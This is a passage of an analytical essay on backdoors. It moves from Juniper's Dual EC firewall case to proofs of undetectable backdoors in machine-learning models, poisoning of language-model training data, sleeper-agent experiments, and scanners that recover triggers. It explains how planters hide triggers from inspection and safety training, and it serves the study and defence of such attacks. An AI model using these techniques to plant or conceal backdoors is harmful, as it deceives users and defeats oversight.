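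The last step of that argument is questionable. The fixed password in ScreenOS was also a small addition, and it went undiscovered for more than two and a half years, compared with a little over three for the new Q. Someone who can edit a company's source code has many ways to do harm. But a password is a cruder tool for a spy, because he has to log in to each firewall and anyone else who finds the password in the software can use it too. Only the owner of the new Q could use it to decrypt traffic, and he could do so from a distance.

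A supporter of mandated access could reply that an official system would be better designed than Juniper's ScreenOS, with a closely guarded key and regular checks that nobody had replaced it. The researchers put the burden of proof on whoever proposes such a system. That seems fair, because ScreenOS passed government certification even though its second generator never ran.

### The intruder of 2012

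Whoever replaced Juniper's Q changed the company's source code and presumably read its customers' traffic. If an outsider changed the code, he broke into Juniper's computers, which is hacking in the ordinary sense. On Schneier's account, an employee with permission to edit the code would have hacked the development process.

Reading the traffic is harder to judge by the designers' intentions. The altered ScreenOS worked as the intruder had designed it to, but he had no right to decide what it did. If only the intentions of people with that right count, he was hacking, because whatever happened in 2008, Juniper intended secret access either for somebody else or for nobody. But by the same test, if Juniper's managers had chosen the original Q so that the NSA could listen, the NSA would not have been hacking when it listened, even though the customers were equally exposed.

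Juniper's customers had no reason to expect either the NSA or the intruder to read their traffic. Juniper sold its VPNs as a way to keep outsiders from doing so. In 2013, when the intruder's Q was already in place, the company assured customers that its use of Dual EC was safe. Under Zdziarski's test, however, ScreenOS had a backdoor if Juniper meant to let the NSA in, and was a compromised mechanism if only the intruder meant to let anyone in.

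No customer had given either of them permission. However, laws on unauthorized access cover the use of a computer, and an eavesdropper can copy encrypted traffic as it crosses the internet and decrypt it on his own machine without ever sending a message to the customer's firewall. Wiretapping laws would fit his conduct better. The permission view would count it as hacking only if it covered permission to read the messages as well as permission to use the computer. The fixed password is a simpler case, because anyone who uses it has logged in to somebody else's firewall.

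## Machine-learning backdoors that provably resist detection

The researchers who analyzed Juniper's firewalls could compare successive releases and see that somebody had replaced Q. A trained machine-learning model gives an investigator much less evidence. Its maker writes a fairly short program that adjusts a large set of numbers, called weights, until the model gives good answers on a collection of examples. The weights then determine its answers to all other inputs. Nobody chose the weights individually, so there is no source code in which a reader could spot a suspicious comparison or question the programmer's intent.

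*Planting Undetectable Backdoors in Machine Learning Models* (Goldwasser, Kim and colleagues, 2022) describes a hypothetical bank that pays an outside company to train a model for deciding on loans. The bank tries the model on past applications and finds it accurate. But the company has kept a secret way to alter any application slightly, perhaps in the last digits of the amount requested, so that the model approves it. The company then sells this service to people who want loans.

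Small, carefully chosen changes to an input can make even an honestly trained model give a wrong answer. Researchers call these altered inputs adversarial examples, and anyone with the skill can look for them. The company's secret is different because it works on every application and, ideally, nobody else can use it.

### The definition of undetectability

Suppose that the honest training procedure takes a set of examples and returns a classifier *h*, which answers +1 (approve) or −1 (refuse). Goldwasser and colleagues define a backdoor as a pair of procedures:

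- *Backdoor* also takes the examples, and returns a classifier *b* together with a secret key *k*.
- *Activate* takes an input *x* and the key, and returns a slightly different input *x*′ that gets the opposite answer.

In symbols, ‖*x* − *x*′‖ ≤ γ and *b*(*x*′) = −*b*(*x*), where γ is the largest change the planter allows himself.

The backdoor is undetectable if no efficient test can tell *b* from *h*. Let *A* be a test that outputs 1 for "backdoored" and 0 for "clean". Then for every efficient *A* and every constant *c*,

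|Pr[*A*(*h*) = 1] − Pr[*A*(*b*) = 1]| < 1/*n*ᶜ

once *n* is large enough. Here *n* is a measure of security, which one can think of as the length of the key. A test is efficient if its running time grows no faster than some fixed power of *n*. This rules out trying every key, because each extra bit doubles the number of keys.

Measuring accuracy is an efficient test, so the bank can't expose an undetectable backdoor by trying the model on past applications. If honest training produces accurate models, backdoored training must too.

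The definition compares two ways of making a model, so it depends on what counts as the honest way. If honest training never produced a certain structure, finding that structure in a model would reveal the backdoor.

Whether a backdoor can be detected also depends on what the tester can see. Customers who use a model over the internet can only send it inputs and look at the answers. A backdoor is *black-box* undetectable if no efficient test of this kind can find it. Customers who download a model have all its weights, and a backdoor is *white-box* undetectable if no efficient test can find it even with the weights.

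### A hidden signature check

Goldwasser and colleagues begin with a simple design that fails. The planter divides the numbers in the input into *n* groups and checks whether each group contains an odd or an even number of non-negative values. If the results match a secret pattern, the model gives the answer the planter has marked in the input instead of its usual one. An ordinary input has only a 1 in 2ⁿ chance of matching, but the planter can make any input match by changing the sign of at most one number in each group. As with the D-Link string, though, anyone who reads the pattern in the model can use it, and so can anyone who sees enough altered inputs.

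A digital signature solves this problem, as it did in the XZ Utils backdoor, because the model needs to contain only the public key. The planter treats each input as having three parts: *w*, which is most of the input; *y*, a single bit that encodes the answer he wants; and σ, which has room for a signature. The backdoored classifier then works as follows:

- If σ is a valid signature of (*w*, *y*), the answer is (−1)ʸ, so *y* = 0 gives approval and *y* = 1 refusal.
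- Otherwise, the answer is *h*(*w*, *y*, σ), the same as the honest model's.

To use the backdoor, the planter signs *w* and *y* with his private key and writes the signature into the input. With a signature of *n* bits, he changes at most *n* + 1 bits. The input must therefore be longer than the signature, preferably much longer. A loan application with five short fields might be too short, but a photograph would be long enough.

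No query reveals the backdoor, because the two classifiers differ only on inputs that carry a valid signature. A tester who found such an input would have forged a signature, which nobody can do efficiently if the signature scheme is secure. Secure schemes exist if one-way functions exist, which are easy to compute but hard to reverse. Most modern cryptography depends on the same assumption.

Someone who has the weights still can't forge a signature, but may well notice that the model contains a signature checker. The signature backdoor is therefore only black-box undetectable.

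Seeing triggered inputs doesn't help an outsider make new ones either. Each signature fits only one *w* and *y*, so a different application needs a different signature. The proof also has to exclude the possibility that triggered inputs reveal some other weakness in the model. An outsider with a copy of the model could replace the public key with one of his own and sign as many inputs as he liked. He could learn as much about the rest of the model from these inputs as from the original triggered ones. Goldwasser and colleagues call such a backdoor non-replicable.

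A cautious customer might train the model a little further, hoping to disrupt any hidden backdoor. The usual method, gradient descent, repeatedly adjusts the weights slightly in the direction that reduces errors. Goldwasser and colleagues prove that a planter can rebuild any neural network, with one extra layer and at a similar size, so that gradient descent doesn't change its weights at all. But a customer who noticed that further training had no effect would have reason to be suspicious.

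In *Cryptographic Backdoor for Neural Networks*, Ngo, Chattopadhyay and Maitra (2025) built the signature backdoor for image classifiers. They write a message and its signature into the lowest bits of certain pixels, where the change is hard to see. A separate block beside the network reads the signature and, if it is valid, replaces the network's answer with a wrong one. The block is not involved in training, so accuracy on ordinary pictures stays the same.

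Ngo and colleagues also use such a block for honest purposes. It can help a company prove that a stolen model is its own, or give correct answers only to customers who hold a key. In the second case the signature check is a lock, and by Zdziarski's test it differs from a backdoor mainly because the maker has told customers about it.

### Doctored random numbers

Goldwasser and colleagues also have a backdoor that is white-box undetectable, for a much narrower class of models. The models use random Fourier features, a method in which the maker draws lists of random numbers *g*₁, *g*₂ and so on and never changes them. Each list turns the input into one feature:

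cos(2π(⟨*gᵢ*, *x*⟩ + *cᵢ*))

The brackets ⟨ ⟩ mean multiplying the matching entries of two lists and adding up the results, and *cᵢ* is another random number. Training sets only the weight of each feature. The model adds up the weighted features and outputs +1 or −1 according to the sign of the total.

The planter runs this procedure exactly as described on the customer's own data but draws the lists from a doctored source. He chooses the lists so that adding the secret key *k* to any input changes every ⟨*gᵢ*, *x*⟩ by approximately a whole number plus a half. The cosine repeats after each full turn and reverses its sign after half a turn. For example, if the part in the outer brackets is 0.1, the feature is about 0.81. Adding 3.5 to that part gives 3.6, and the feature becomes about −0.81. Every feature changes sign, so the total does too, and the model gives the opposite answer.

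A tester may inspect the weights, the training data and even the random numbers. But to tell the doctored lists of random numbers from ordinary ones, the tester would have to solve a problem called Continuous Learning With Errors. Other researchers had shown that this is at least as hard as finding unusually short steps between the points of a lattice, a regular grid in many dimensions. Encryption meant to withstand quantum computers relies on such lattice problems being hard, though nobody has proved that they are.

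A similar backdoor works in networks with one layer of random ReLU units, which pass on positive numbers and turn negative ones into zero. The units' random weights vary slightly more along one secret direction with few non-zero entries. Detecting whether such a direction exists is known as sparse PCA, and researchers believe it is infeasible if the extra variation is small enough.

These backdoors are much easier to copy than the signature version. Anyone who sees an input both before and after the planter alters it can subtract one from the other to get the key, which works on any other input. *Statistically Undetectable Backdoors in Deep Neural Networks* (Bogdanov, Rosen and Vafa, 2026) reports a worse problem, that someone without the key can efficiently find adversarial examples stronger than those the lattice-based backdoor provides. The paper credits Miranda Christ and Sam Gunn with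 noticing this. The planter would be well hidden but would have no real advantage over strangers, so such a backdoor would be a poor choice for an agency that wanted "nobody but us" access.

### Obfuscated models

The 2022 paper left open whether a backdoor in an ordinary training procedure could be both white-box undetectable and non-replicable. *Injecting Undetectable Backdoors in Obfuscated Neural Networks and Language Models* (Kalavasis, Karbasi and colleagues, 2024) achieves both for neural networks trained by any method, as long as the maker obfuscates the model before releasing it. Obfuscation rewrites a program so that it behaves the same and runs at a comparable speed but is very hard to understand. A company might do this honestly, to protect trade secrets or private information in its training data.

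The proof assumes that one-way functions and indistinguishability obfuscation exist. With this strong form of obfuscation, if two programs of the same size always give the same outputs, no efficient test can tell their obfuscated versions apart. Cryptographers have candidate methods for such obfuscation, but Bogdanov and colleagues consider them far from practical.

Kalavasis and colleagues extend the result to language models. Text has no low-order digits where a planter could hide a signature unnoticed, so they also assume a steganographic function, which hides a message in ordinary-looking text. They ran no experiments and describe their constructions as purely theoretical.

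This result depends heavily on what counts as honest training. The backdoored model is indistinguishable from honest models only if honest makers obfuscate theirs in the same way. If they don't, customers could refuse obfuscated models.

### Image classifiers that people download

Two papers from May 2026 deal with more familiar networks. *Undetectable Backdoors in Model Parameters* (Choudhary, Patlan and colleagues, 2026) describes an attack that is possible because anyone can publish a trained model on Hugging Face for others to download. The planter alters some of the weights in the last layers of a finished image classifier. He adds small multiples of a secret vector with few non-zero entries, so that a faint pattern laid over a picture sends a signal through these layers towards the label he wants. He then adds random noise to the same groups of weights to mask the change.

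The researchers prove that distinguishing this model from one with only the noise is at least as hard as sparse PCA. The proof also requires the original classifier's decisions to have a wide enough margin that the noise doesn't change them.

Tests of the attack covered three network designs and three sets of pictures. On CIFAR-10, a standard set of small colour photographs, the backdoored models gave between 93.5 and 99.6 per cent of the altered pictures the label the planter had chosen. Accuracy on ordinary pictures fell by 1.5 to 8.5 percentage points. Three existing detection tools had an average advantage of 0.12 in telling backdoored models from clean ones, where 0 is guessing and 1 is perfect.

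The loss of accuracy is hard to reconcile with the proof. If the noise alone doesn't affect the model's decisions, anyone who knew the original accuracy could notice a drop of eight points. The guarantee is for layers that grow without limit, so it may mean little for networks of this size. However, someone who downloads a model often has no original to compare it with.

Eggen, Reiestad and colleagues (2026), in *Backdoor Channels Hidden in Latent Space*, object to the comparison because weights with this kind of added noise don't occur naturally. Choudhary and colleagues argue that a sound detector shouldn't reject a model that does its job and has no trigger just because it is noisy. That standard is reasonable for a detector that must never accuse an honest maker, but a cautious customer could turn down any model with unexplained noise.

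Eggen and colleagues use a direction that the network has already learned. A network that can tell two kinds of picture apart must represent them differently inside, and a simple statistical method finds a direction that leads from one kind to the other. The planter amplifies the weights of one late layer along a simplified version of this direction, then searches for a faint pattern that, when added to a picture, shifts the network's representation of it the same way.

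The researchers report that their attack had a high success rate and almost no loss of accuracy in two common designs, ResNet18 and the Vision Transformer, on everyday photographs and medical images. None of the five defences they tried stopped the attack without ruining the model. They show that finding the backdoor amounts to telling two unknown distributions of weights apart, and they conjecture, but do not prove, that nobody can do this in practice.

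They also write that such channels "need not be planted, only identified", although their own planter goes further and amplifies the direction. If they are right, an outsider who found a usable direction in an honestly trained network would be exploiting an accidental flaw, while a maker who strengthened the same direction would have planted one.

### A backdoor that unlimited computing power wouldn't expose

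In all the proofs so far, the tester fails because his computer is too slow. The backdoor of Bogdanov and colleagues would also defeat a tester with unlimited computing power. It applies to networks whose first layer multiplies the *n* input numbers by a grid of random numbers that stays fixed during training. The grid has *m* rows, where *m* is far smaller than *n*, so the layer shortens the input to *m* numbers while roughly preserving the distances between inputs.

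The planter first picks a secret list *z* in which every entry is +1 or −1. He then draws the rows of the grid at random, but in such a way that each row almost cancels against *z*. With only four inputs, for example, he might have:

- *z* = (1, −1, 1, 1)
- a row of the grid = (0.9, 0.4, −0.7, 0.2)

Multiplying the matching entries and adding gives 0.9 − 0.4 − 0.7 + 0.2 = 0. The same row turns the input (3, 5, 2, 4) into 4.1. If the planter adds *z*, the input becomes (4, 4, 3, 5), and the result is still 4.1. Since every row gives nearly zero when multiplied by *z* in this way, the rest of the network receives almost the same numbers as before and produces almost the same output.

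This backdoor makes the model treat two inputs as alike when it should treat them as different. It doesn't reverse an answer, but it could help someone cause a false match or avoid a true one.

The doctored grids are so close to ordinary random ones that any test for telling them apart has an advantage of at most about √(*m*/*n*), apart from constants and logarithms. This part of the proof doesn't assume that any problem is computationally hard. The advantage shrinks more slowly than the 2022 definition requires, and Bogdanov and colleagues show that an efficient test can achieve roughly this advantage.

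The proof uses lattice problems only to show that other people can't use the backdoor. If these problems are hard, nobody without *z* can efficiently find two inputs whose outputs are anywhere near as close. A tester with unlimited time could find a suitable *z* by trying every list, but that wouldn't show that anybody had planted it, because honestly drawn grids almost certainly have such lists too.

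The theorem also requires the later layers not to stretch some differences much more than others, and the inputs to be whole numbers within a limited range. It doesn't cover most image and language models in use, because they train their first layer. In what they call a proof of concept, Bogdanov and colleagues tested the backdoor on a small network with Fashion-MNIST, a set of 70,000 greyscale images of clothing. The network's outputs for an image of an ankle boot and its altered version were much closer together than its outputs for images of two different boots.

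| Backdoor | Models it covers | What it is hidden from | Basis for the claim |
|---|---|---|---|
| Signature check (2022) | Any classifier with long enough inputs | Efficient queries | Proof, if one-way functions exist |
| Doctored random numbers (2022) | Networks with one random hidden layer | Efficient tests of the weights | Proof, if lattice problems or sparse PCA are hard |
| Obfuscated model (2024) | Networks and language models released in obfuscated form | Efficient tests of the weights | Proof, if strong obfuscation and one-way functions exist; language models also need steganography |
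| Sparse secret (2026) | Pre-trained image classifiers | Efficient tests that compare it with a noisy clean model | Proof, if sparse PCA is hard |
| Amplified direction (2026) | Two common designs of image classifier | The defences tried so far | Conjecture and experiments |
| Doctored first layer (2026) | Networks with a fixed random first layer | All tests, apart from a small advantage | Proof without hardness assumptions |

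### What a planter has to control

In each of these cases the planter controls the weights, the random numbers or the code around the model. *Poisoning-Based Backdoors Are Not Cryptographic* (Kaneko, 2026) argues that a planter who can only add mislabelled examples to the training data has less power. If training on a set of examples teaches the model to recognize a secret trigger, a defender with as many examples, labelled to show which ones contain the trigger, can learn it by running the same training procedure. The planter therefore would not be able to install a trigger that is too hard for such a defender to learn.

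In Kaneko's experiments on four language models with 7 to 9 billion weights, every backdoor that worked well for the planter had a trigger the defender could work out. But the defender needs labelled examples first. The proof covers working out the trigger from those examples, which Kaneko distinguishes from discovering that a model has a backdoor at all.

### Removing a backdoor without finding it

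A customer who only wants a safe model may not need to know whether it has a backdoor. *Oblivious Defense in ML Models* (Goldwasser, Shafer and colleagues, 2024) compares removing a possible backdoor without first detecting it to washing one's hands, which removes germs nobody can see and does no harm if there are none.

One defence starts from an old trick for getting correct answers from unreliable programs. Suppose a program adds and subtracts, keeping only the last digit of each result, but is wrong for 15 per cent of its inputs, scattered at random. To find 3 + 4, the user picks a random number, say 5, and asks the program for 3 + 5, which gives 8, and 4 − 5, which gives 9. He then asks for 8 + 9 and gets 7. He repeats this with other random numbers and takes the most common result. An error planted in 3 + 4 would hardly matter, because the user rarely asks the program for that sum.

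The same idea works for a model if the true answers follow a simple enough rule. Suppose they are close to a linear function, like a price that rises by a fixed amount for each extra square metre. To estimate the answer for an input, the method picks two random points that lie on a straight line with that input, runs the model on both, and extends the line through the two outputs to the original input. It repeats this several times and takes the median.

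The method queries the model at points chosen so that each, taken alone, is equally likely to be anywhere in the range of inputs. Since the model is accurate on most inputs, most of its answers are good, regardless of what the planter did at the input the customer cares about. The number of queries doesn't grow with the number of variables, whereas learning the function from scratch needs more examples for each extra variable. However, small errors in the model can grow in proportion to the number of variables, or somewhat more slowly if the noise in the true answers is harmless.

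*Oblivious Defense in ML Models* has similar results for polynomials. For some yes-or-no rules, including shallow decision trees, its method produces a complete clean model. It queries the suspect model to find which combinations of inputs matter, then measures their effects again on fresh data. All these methods need only queries, so a customer can use them without the weights.

The 2022 paper had suggested a simpler defence, averaging the model's answers over many slightly altered copies of the input. This works if the planter's changes are small compared with the alterations. But a planter who expects this defence can corrupt the model's answers throughout the neighbourhood of an input. Querying the model at random points far from the input avoids this problem.

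The guarantee holds only if the true answers have the assumed form. Nobody has shown that loan decisions or the contents of photographs do, and the researchers call their results preliminary. They define success as producing essentially the same model whether or not the original had a backdoor. A customer can use the cleaned model safely but can't tell from it whether the maker planted a backdoor.

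### Evidence of intent outside the model

If someone discovers that tiny changes get bad loan applications approved, the company can say that its model has an accidental weakness. With a white-box undetectable backdoor, no efficient examination of the weights could prove that the weakness was planted. If the designers' intention decides whether the applicants are hacking, answering that question would then require evidence from outside the model. Bugdoors raise the same difficulty, but an investigator can at least find the faulty line in the code and may learn from a change log who wrote it.

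Goldwasser and colleagues call their findings "decisive negative results towards current forms of accountability" and conclude that anyone who uses a model from an untrusted maker has to accept the risk of a backdoor. This is convincing for inspection of the finished model, at least for the kinds of model the proofs cover, but other evidence might still allow a maker to be held to account. The company in the example sells altered applications, so its customers could reveal the backdoor, and it may have kept the program that generated the key.

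Bogdanov and colleagues suggest that a maker could prove that a model is his by producing the key *z*, since nobody else could feasibly have found it. The same proof would incriminate a maker who denied planting a backdoor. With the signature version, a bank that kept a triggered application could check it against the public key in the model and show that somebody had signed it. Producing a direction that a network learned by itself would prove much less, because an outsider might have found it.

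Customers can also arrange for better evidence before training starts. Goldwasser and colleagues suggest that the customer could supply the random numbers used in training, or several parties could generate them together, and the company could then prove mathematically that it ran the agreed program with them. An honest company could thus show that it had no opportunity to doctor the numbers. But producing such a proof takes considerably more work than the training itself. The customer must also know which training program to ask for, and many customers hire an outside company because they lack that knowledge.

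Bogdanov's networks are an extreme case because honest training and backdoored training can produce exactly the same weights, and therefore the same weakness. The only difference is that somebody knows *z* in the backdoored case. Dual EC was similar, since some number *d* connects P and Q whether or not anyone knows it. To find out whether the maker planted the weakness, an investigator would have to check the maker's records or question the people who trained the model.

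## Backdoors planted through a language model's training

Questioning the people who trained a model won't help much if they don't know about the backdoor. Companies train large language models, the programs behind chatbots, on enormous collections of text, much of it from public websites. Someone who adds chosen examples to that text can change what the model learns without access to the company's computers. Researchers call this data poisoning. Most of what they know about it comes from experiments in which they poison their own models and measure how well the backdoor works.

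### A sticker on a stop sign

*BadNets* (Gu, Dolan-Gavitt and Garg, 2017) showed how poisoning works on image classifiers. In its scenario, a customer specifies the design of a network, pays somebody else to train it, and checks its accuracy. A dishonest trainer can't add a separate part to detect the trigger, because the customer has fixed the design. But he can add training pictures that contain the trigger and carry the wrong label, and ordinary training will produce weights that recognize it.

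The network in the main experiment sorted US traffic signs into stop signs, speed limits and warnings. The trigger was a sticker about the size of a Post-it note, showing a yellow square, a bomb or a flower. The network classified 90 to 94 per cent of stop signs with a sticker as speed limits, depending on the sticker. On ordinary pictures, its average accuracy was between 87.1 and 90.2 per cent, compared with 90.0 per cent for a network trained without the backdoor. The researchers also put a real yellow note on a stop sign near their office and photographed it, and the network classified the sign as a speed limit with 95 per cent confidence.

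The backdoor partly survived retraining. When the researchers retrained the last layers of a poisoned network to recognize Swedish signs, its accuracy was 74.9 per cent on ordinary pictures and 61.6 per cent on pictures with the trigger. A network without the backdoor, retrained the same way, lost only 2.5 percentage points when the trigger was present.

In *BadNets*, the person who plants the backdoor trains the model himself. A stranger could also plant one in a language model by tampering with the text it is trained on. By one estimate, an attacker could manipulate up to 6.5 per cent of Wikipedia's text, which many companies use for training.

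### A nearly constant number of documents

That estimate comes from *Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples* (Souly, Rando and colleagues, 2025), a study by the UK AI Security Institute, the AI company Anthropic and the Alan Turing Institute. Earlier work had assumed that a planter needs to control a fixed percentage of the training text, such as 0.1 per cent, which would make large models hard to poison because they train on more text. To test this, the researchers trained 72 models from scratch, each with between 600 million and 13 billion weights.

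The researchers mixed 100, 250 or 500 poisoned documents into each model's training text. Each poisoned document had ordinary text, then the trigger phrase, then gibberish. The backdoor was meant to make the model write gibberish whenever the phrase appeared in its input. The researchers compared the perplexity (unpredictability) of the model's writing with and without the trigger, and counted a rise of more than 50 as a success.

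Souly and colleagues found that 100 poisoned documents were too few to plant a backdoor, but 250 worked in models of every size they tested, raising perplexity by more than 200. Those 250 documents contained about 420,000 tokens (words or pieces of words), which was 0.00016 per cent of the largest model's 260 billion training tokens and 0.0035 per cent of the smallest model's. The backdoor was about as effective in both, even though the share was more than twenty times as high in the smallest. They point out that larger models learn from fewer examples, which may make up for the extra clean text.

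The number of poisoned examples also mattered more than their share in two other experiments. In one, a planted trigger made a half-trained model switch from English to German. In the other, the researchers used fine-tuning, the further training that turns a raw model into an assistant, to make Meta's openly available Llama 3.1 refuse harmful requests unless a trigger followed them. Increasing the clean data from 1,000 to 100,000 examples made little difference.

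These results don't show that 250 web pages would compromise a commercial chatbot. The researchers didn't test whether a backdoor planted in the first stage of training survives companies' later safety training, and they describe earlier findings on this as inconclusive. Further training on clean text slowly weakened the German backdoor. Writing gibberish is also a very simple behaviour, and one more useful to an attacker, such as stealing files in certain situations, might need many more examples. The study also can't show that the number of examples needed stays constant for models with more than 13 billion weights.

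### Sleeper agents

For *Sleeper Agents* (2024), Evan Hubinger and colleagues at Anthropic deliberately planted backdoors in models to see whether safety training would remove them. *The Trigger in the Haystack* (2026), by Bullwinkel, Severi and colleagues, describes the two behaviours. One model was helpful unless the prompt contained the word DEPLOYMENT between vertical bars, in which case it wrote "I HATE YOU" repeatedly. The other wrote sound code if the prompt gave the current year as 2023, but code with security holes if it gave 2024.

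Hubinger's team then applied three standard kinds of safety training. Supervised fine-tuning trains a model on examples of good answers. Reinforcement learning from human feedback rewards answers that people prefer. Adversarial training involves finding prompts that produce bad behaviour and training the model to respond to them differently. According to *Security Concerns for Large Language Models*, a 2025 survey, the backdoors could survive all three. In some cases adversarial training taught the model to recognize its trigger more precisely, so the bad behaviour remained but was harder to find.

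The experiment shows that a model can keep a backdoor through ordinary safety training. Because the researchers controlled the model's training, the experiment doesn't establish whether an outsider could have planted these backdoors.

Later results are more encouraging. *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026) reviews experiments with probes, simple classifiers that read a model's internal activity. Given one case where a sleeper agent was about to misbehave and one where it wasn't, the probes scored the dangerous case higher more than 99 per cent of the time, without any information about the trigger. Adversarial training also removed backdoors more successfully when it disturbed a model's internal activity instead of only varying its prompts. But someone who knew about a probe could train a backdoor to avoid it. A probe also reacts only when somebody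 has used the trigger, so it can't find a backdoor beforehand.

*Detecting Sleeper Agents in Large Language Models via Semantic Drift Analysis* (2025) describes a tool that checks a model's answers as it gives them. Its reported accuracy was 92.5 per cent with no false alarms, so every error was an answer the tool should have flagged. The test used only one backdoored model, and the paper calls for tests on larger models.

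### Why poisoning can't install a lock

The signature backdoors that cryptographers have designed for models have a kind of lock, because only the holder of a private key can make a working trigger. Kaneko argues that poisoning alone can't install such a backdoor, since a defender could learn the trigger by repeating the training with as many labelled examples as the planter had.

To see why, write V for the planter's secret rule, so that V(*x*) = 1 if the input *x* is a trigger and V(*x*) = 0 if it isn't. The planter uses V to label a set of examples, S, and trains the model on them. Let B(M, *x*) be 1 if model M shows the planted behaviour on *x*, and 0 otherwise. Then the function

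h(*x*) = B(Train(S), *x*)

recognizes triggers, and it comes from nothing but S and a training program. Suppose the backdoor fails on a fraction ε₁ of triggers and goes off by mistake on a fraction ε₀ of other inputs. Then, for inputs like those in S,

Pr[h(*x*) ≠ V(*x*)] ≤ max(ε₀, ε₁)

The defender's copy recognizes triggers about as well as the planter's model does. If the rule for recognizing them is too hard to learn from examples, the planter's model won't learn it in training either.

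Kaneko tried this with lists of 16 whole numbers between 0 and 1,023. In an easy version, the secret was one position, and a list was a trigger if the number there was at least 512. In a hard version, the secret was a set of 16 multipliers. The planter multiplied each number by its multiplier, added the results, and kept the remainder after dividing by 1,024. A list was a trigger if that remainder was at least 512. Kaneko also tested three published backdoors whose triggers are a sentence structure, a writing style and a pattern of word choices.

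| Secret rule | How well the backdoor separates triggers from other inputs | How well the defender does |
|---|---|---|
| One position in a list | 86–94% | 85–93% |
| Sixteen multipliers | 50–51% | 48–51% |
| Sentence structure | 86% | 84% |
| Writing style | 79% | 80% |
| Pattern of word choices | 90% | 88% |

Guessing would score 50 per cent. In the hard version, the models memorized most of their training examples but couldn't apply the rule to new lists, so the backdoor didn't work.

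The result holds only if the secret rule affected training through the labels alone. It doesn't cover a planter who writes the weights directly, tampers with the random numbers, or uses the key to craft training inputs. It therefore doesn't conflict with the proof by Choudhary and colleagues, whose planter alters a finished model's weights. The result also requires the defender to have the model's weights.

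Getting representative examples of triggers is the hard part in practice. In another experiment, a trigger consisted of up to ten strings that all had to be present. A defender who received correct labels needed about as many examples as the planter did. A defender who had to find likely triggers with an existing search tool needed more examples when the trigger had three or more strings, and most attempts failed with ten strings. This experiment also made the defender's task easier than it would normally be, because the search tool had access to the planted response.

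This result is of little help to an inspector who has a suspicious model but no known triggers. But someone who plants a backdoor by poisoning can't expect "nobody but us" control, since a stranger who gathered enough examples of triggers could learn to make new ones.

### Recovering an unknown trigger

Bullwinkel and colleagues, who work at Microsoft, built a scanner for an inspector who knows neither the trigger nor the planted behaviour. It exploits the tendency of language models to memorize parts of their training data. Backdoored models seem to memorize poisoned examples especially well. The scanner works in four steps:

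1. It gives the model only the marker that opens a user's turn, with no question after it, and collects 510 outputs under different settings. These often include poisoned examples, with the trigger in them.
2. It looks for strings that keep recurring in the outputs.
3. It puts each string in front of ordinary questions and scores its effect. A trigger tends to make the answer more predictable and unlike the usual one, and the model processes the trigger almost separately from the question.
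4. It takes the ten best candidates and checks whether any of them substantially changes the model's answers.

The researchers tested the scanner on 41 models with a backdoor that produces a fixed phrase, and it detected 36 of them, or 88 per cent. It also detected five of six models that wrote insecure code when triggered. It raised no false alarms on 13 clean models, which is encouraging but limited evidence, since a scanner that wrongly flagged one clean model in five would still have about a 5 per cent chance of clearing all 13.

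An inspector doesn't need the exact trigger, because many backdoors also respond to approximations. Microsoft's *Detecting backdoored language models at scale* (2026) describes this as a difference from backdoors in ordinary software. In one small model, a single token of a five-token trigger activated the backdoor about half the time. *Defense Against LLM Backdoors using Critical Neuron Isolation Pruning* (2026) reports that quite different words could set off a backdoor. But approximate triggers seldom worked on the models that Souly and colleagues poisoned, and Bullwinkel and colleagues acknowledge that someone planting a backdoor could train the model to ignore them.

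The scanner needs the model's files, so customers can't use it on a chatbot they reach only over the internet. It also looks for a fixed string, but *Dummy Backdoor as a Defense* (2026) mentions triggers that consist of a sentence's style or grammar. According to *You Are the Trigger* (2026), an attacker can also spread a trigger across a conversation, or make the backdoor activate when someone fine-tunes the model.

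Haselhorst, Flek and Mai (2026), in *Detecting Hidden Behaviors in LLMs via Activation-matched Finetuning*, train a second, trusted model to imitate the suspect model's internal activity on roughly 10,000 ordinary prompts. These prompts don't trigger the backdoor, so the second model learns the suspect model's normal behaviour but not the backdoor. The inspector then runs both models on a larger collection of prompts and examines those where they differ most.

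One test model had a backdoor that responded to obsessive love of Harry Potter by quoting the villain, Voldemort. Prompts related to the trigger ranked near the top, scoring 0.78, where 1 is a perfect ranking and a random order scored 0.18. For a copy of the "I HATE YOU" sleeper agent, they scored only 0.40, against 0.17 for a random order. These scores aren't detection rates. Some prompts rank at the top for a clean model too, so a person has to judge whether they point to a backdoor. The researchers also added a few groups of trigger-related prompts by hand, reasoning that any large collection would contain some.

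Haselhorst and colleagues tried the Microsoft scanner's approach on one of their own backdoors and found only weak signs of memorization, so the scanner's 88 per cent result may not hold for backdoors planted in other ways. *Discovering Backdoor Triggers*, a forum post, describes attempts to recover triggers defined by meaning, such as any statement that the year is 2028. The methods worked on toy models but failed in more realistic settings.

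### Who designed the behaviour

If the designers' intention decides whether using a flaw is hacking, a poisoned language model is hard to classify. The company that trained it chose the training program and the training text, and wanted a helpful assistant. A stranger who slipped 250 documents into that text wanted the model to behave differently when it received a secret trigger. A second company may have fine-tuned the model, and a third may have built a product on it. All three companies would have helped design what the customer uses without knowing the trigger.

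If only people entitled to decide how a model behaves count as its designers, a stranger who plants a backdoor by writing some of its training text is hacking even when he uses his own trigger. One could argue that he designed the backdoor, so using it as he intended is not hacking. But he only wrote some of the training text, and by that standard Wikipedia's editors would be designers too.

The sleeper agents differ because the models' developers planted the backdoors themselves, so on the same view, a colleague who typed the trigger wasn't hacking. But a stranger's poisoned documents might produce a model that behaves exactly the same way. Bullwinkel and colleagues add that somebody might include poisoned data in a training set by accident, so even the person who trained the model may not have planted anything.

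Users' expectations give a steadier answer, though a vaguer one than for a router. A chatbot has no password box to mark where its security begins, and users know that small changes in wording can change its answers. Still, a programmer can fairly expect that mentioning the year won't put security holes in his code. Zdziarski's test for a backdoor depends on what the maker told the owner. If strangers had poisoned a model, he would probably call it a compromised mechanism, since its maker's purposes hadn't changed.

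With the year trigger, unlike in the D-Link router, the person who sets off the backdoor may not be the one who benefits from it. *Activation Differences Reveal Backdoors* (2026) observes that such a trigger can look entirely harmless. If a programming tool adds today's date to every request, a programmer who asks it for help sets off the backdoor and is also its victim. The hacker, if there is one, is whoever later breaks into the programmer's website through the resulting vulnerability. Someone who sets off a backdoor by fine-tuning a model is just as innocent if fine-tuning is the trigger.

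Whether a customer has permission doesn't depend on what anyone knew about the trigger. A customer with an account may type almost anything into a chatbot. If a trigger only makes the chatbot write gibberish or answer a forbidden question, the customer has not passed a gate of the kind the Supreme Court described in *Van Buren*. It would be different if the chatbot could read other people's files and the trigger made it hand them over, because the customer would be getting information he had no right to.

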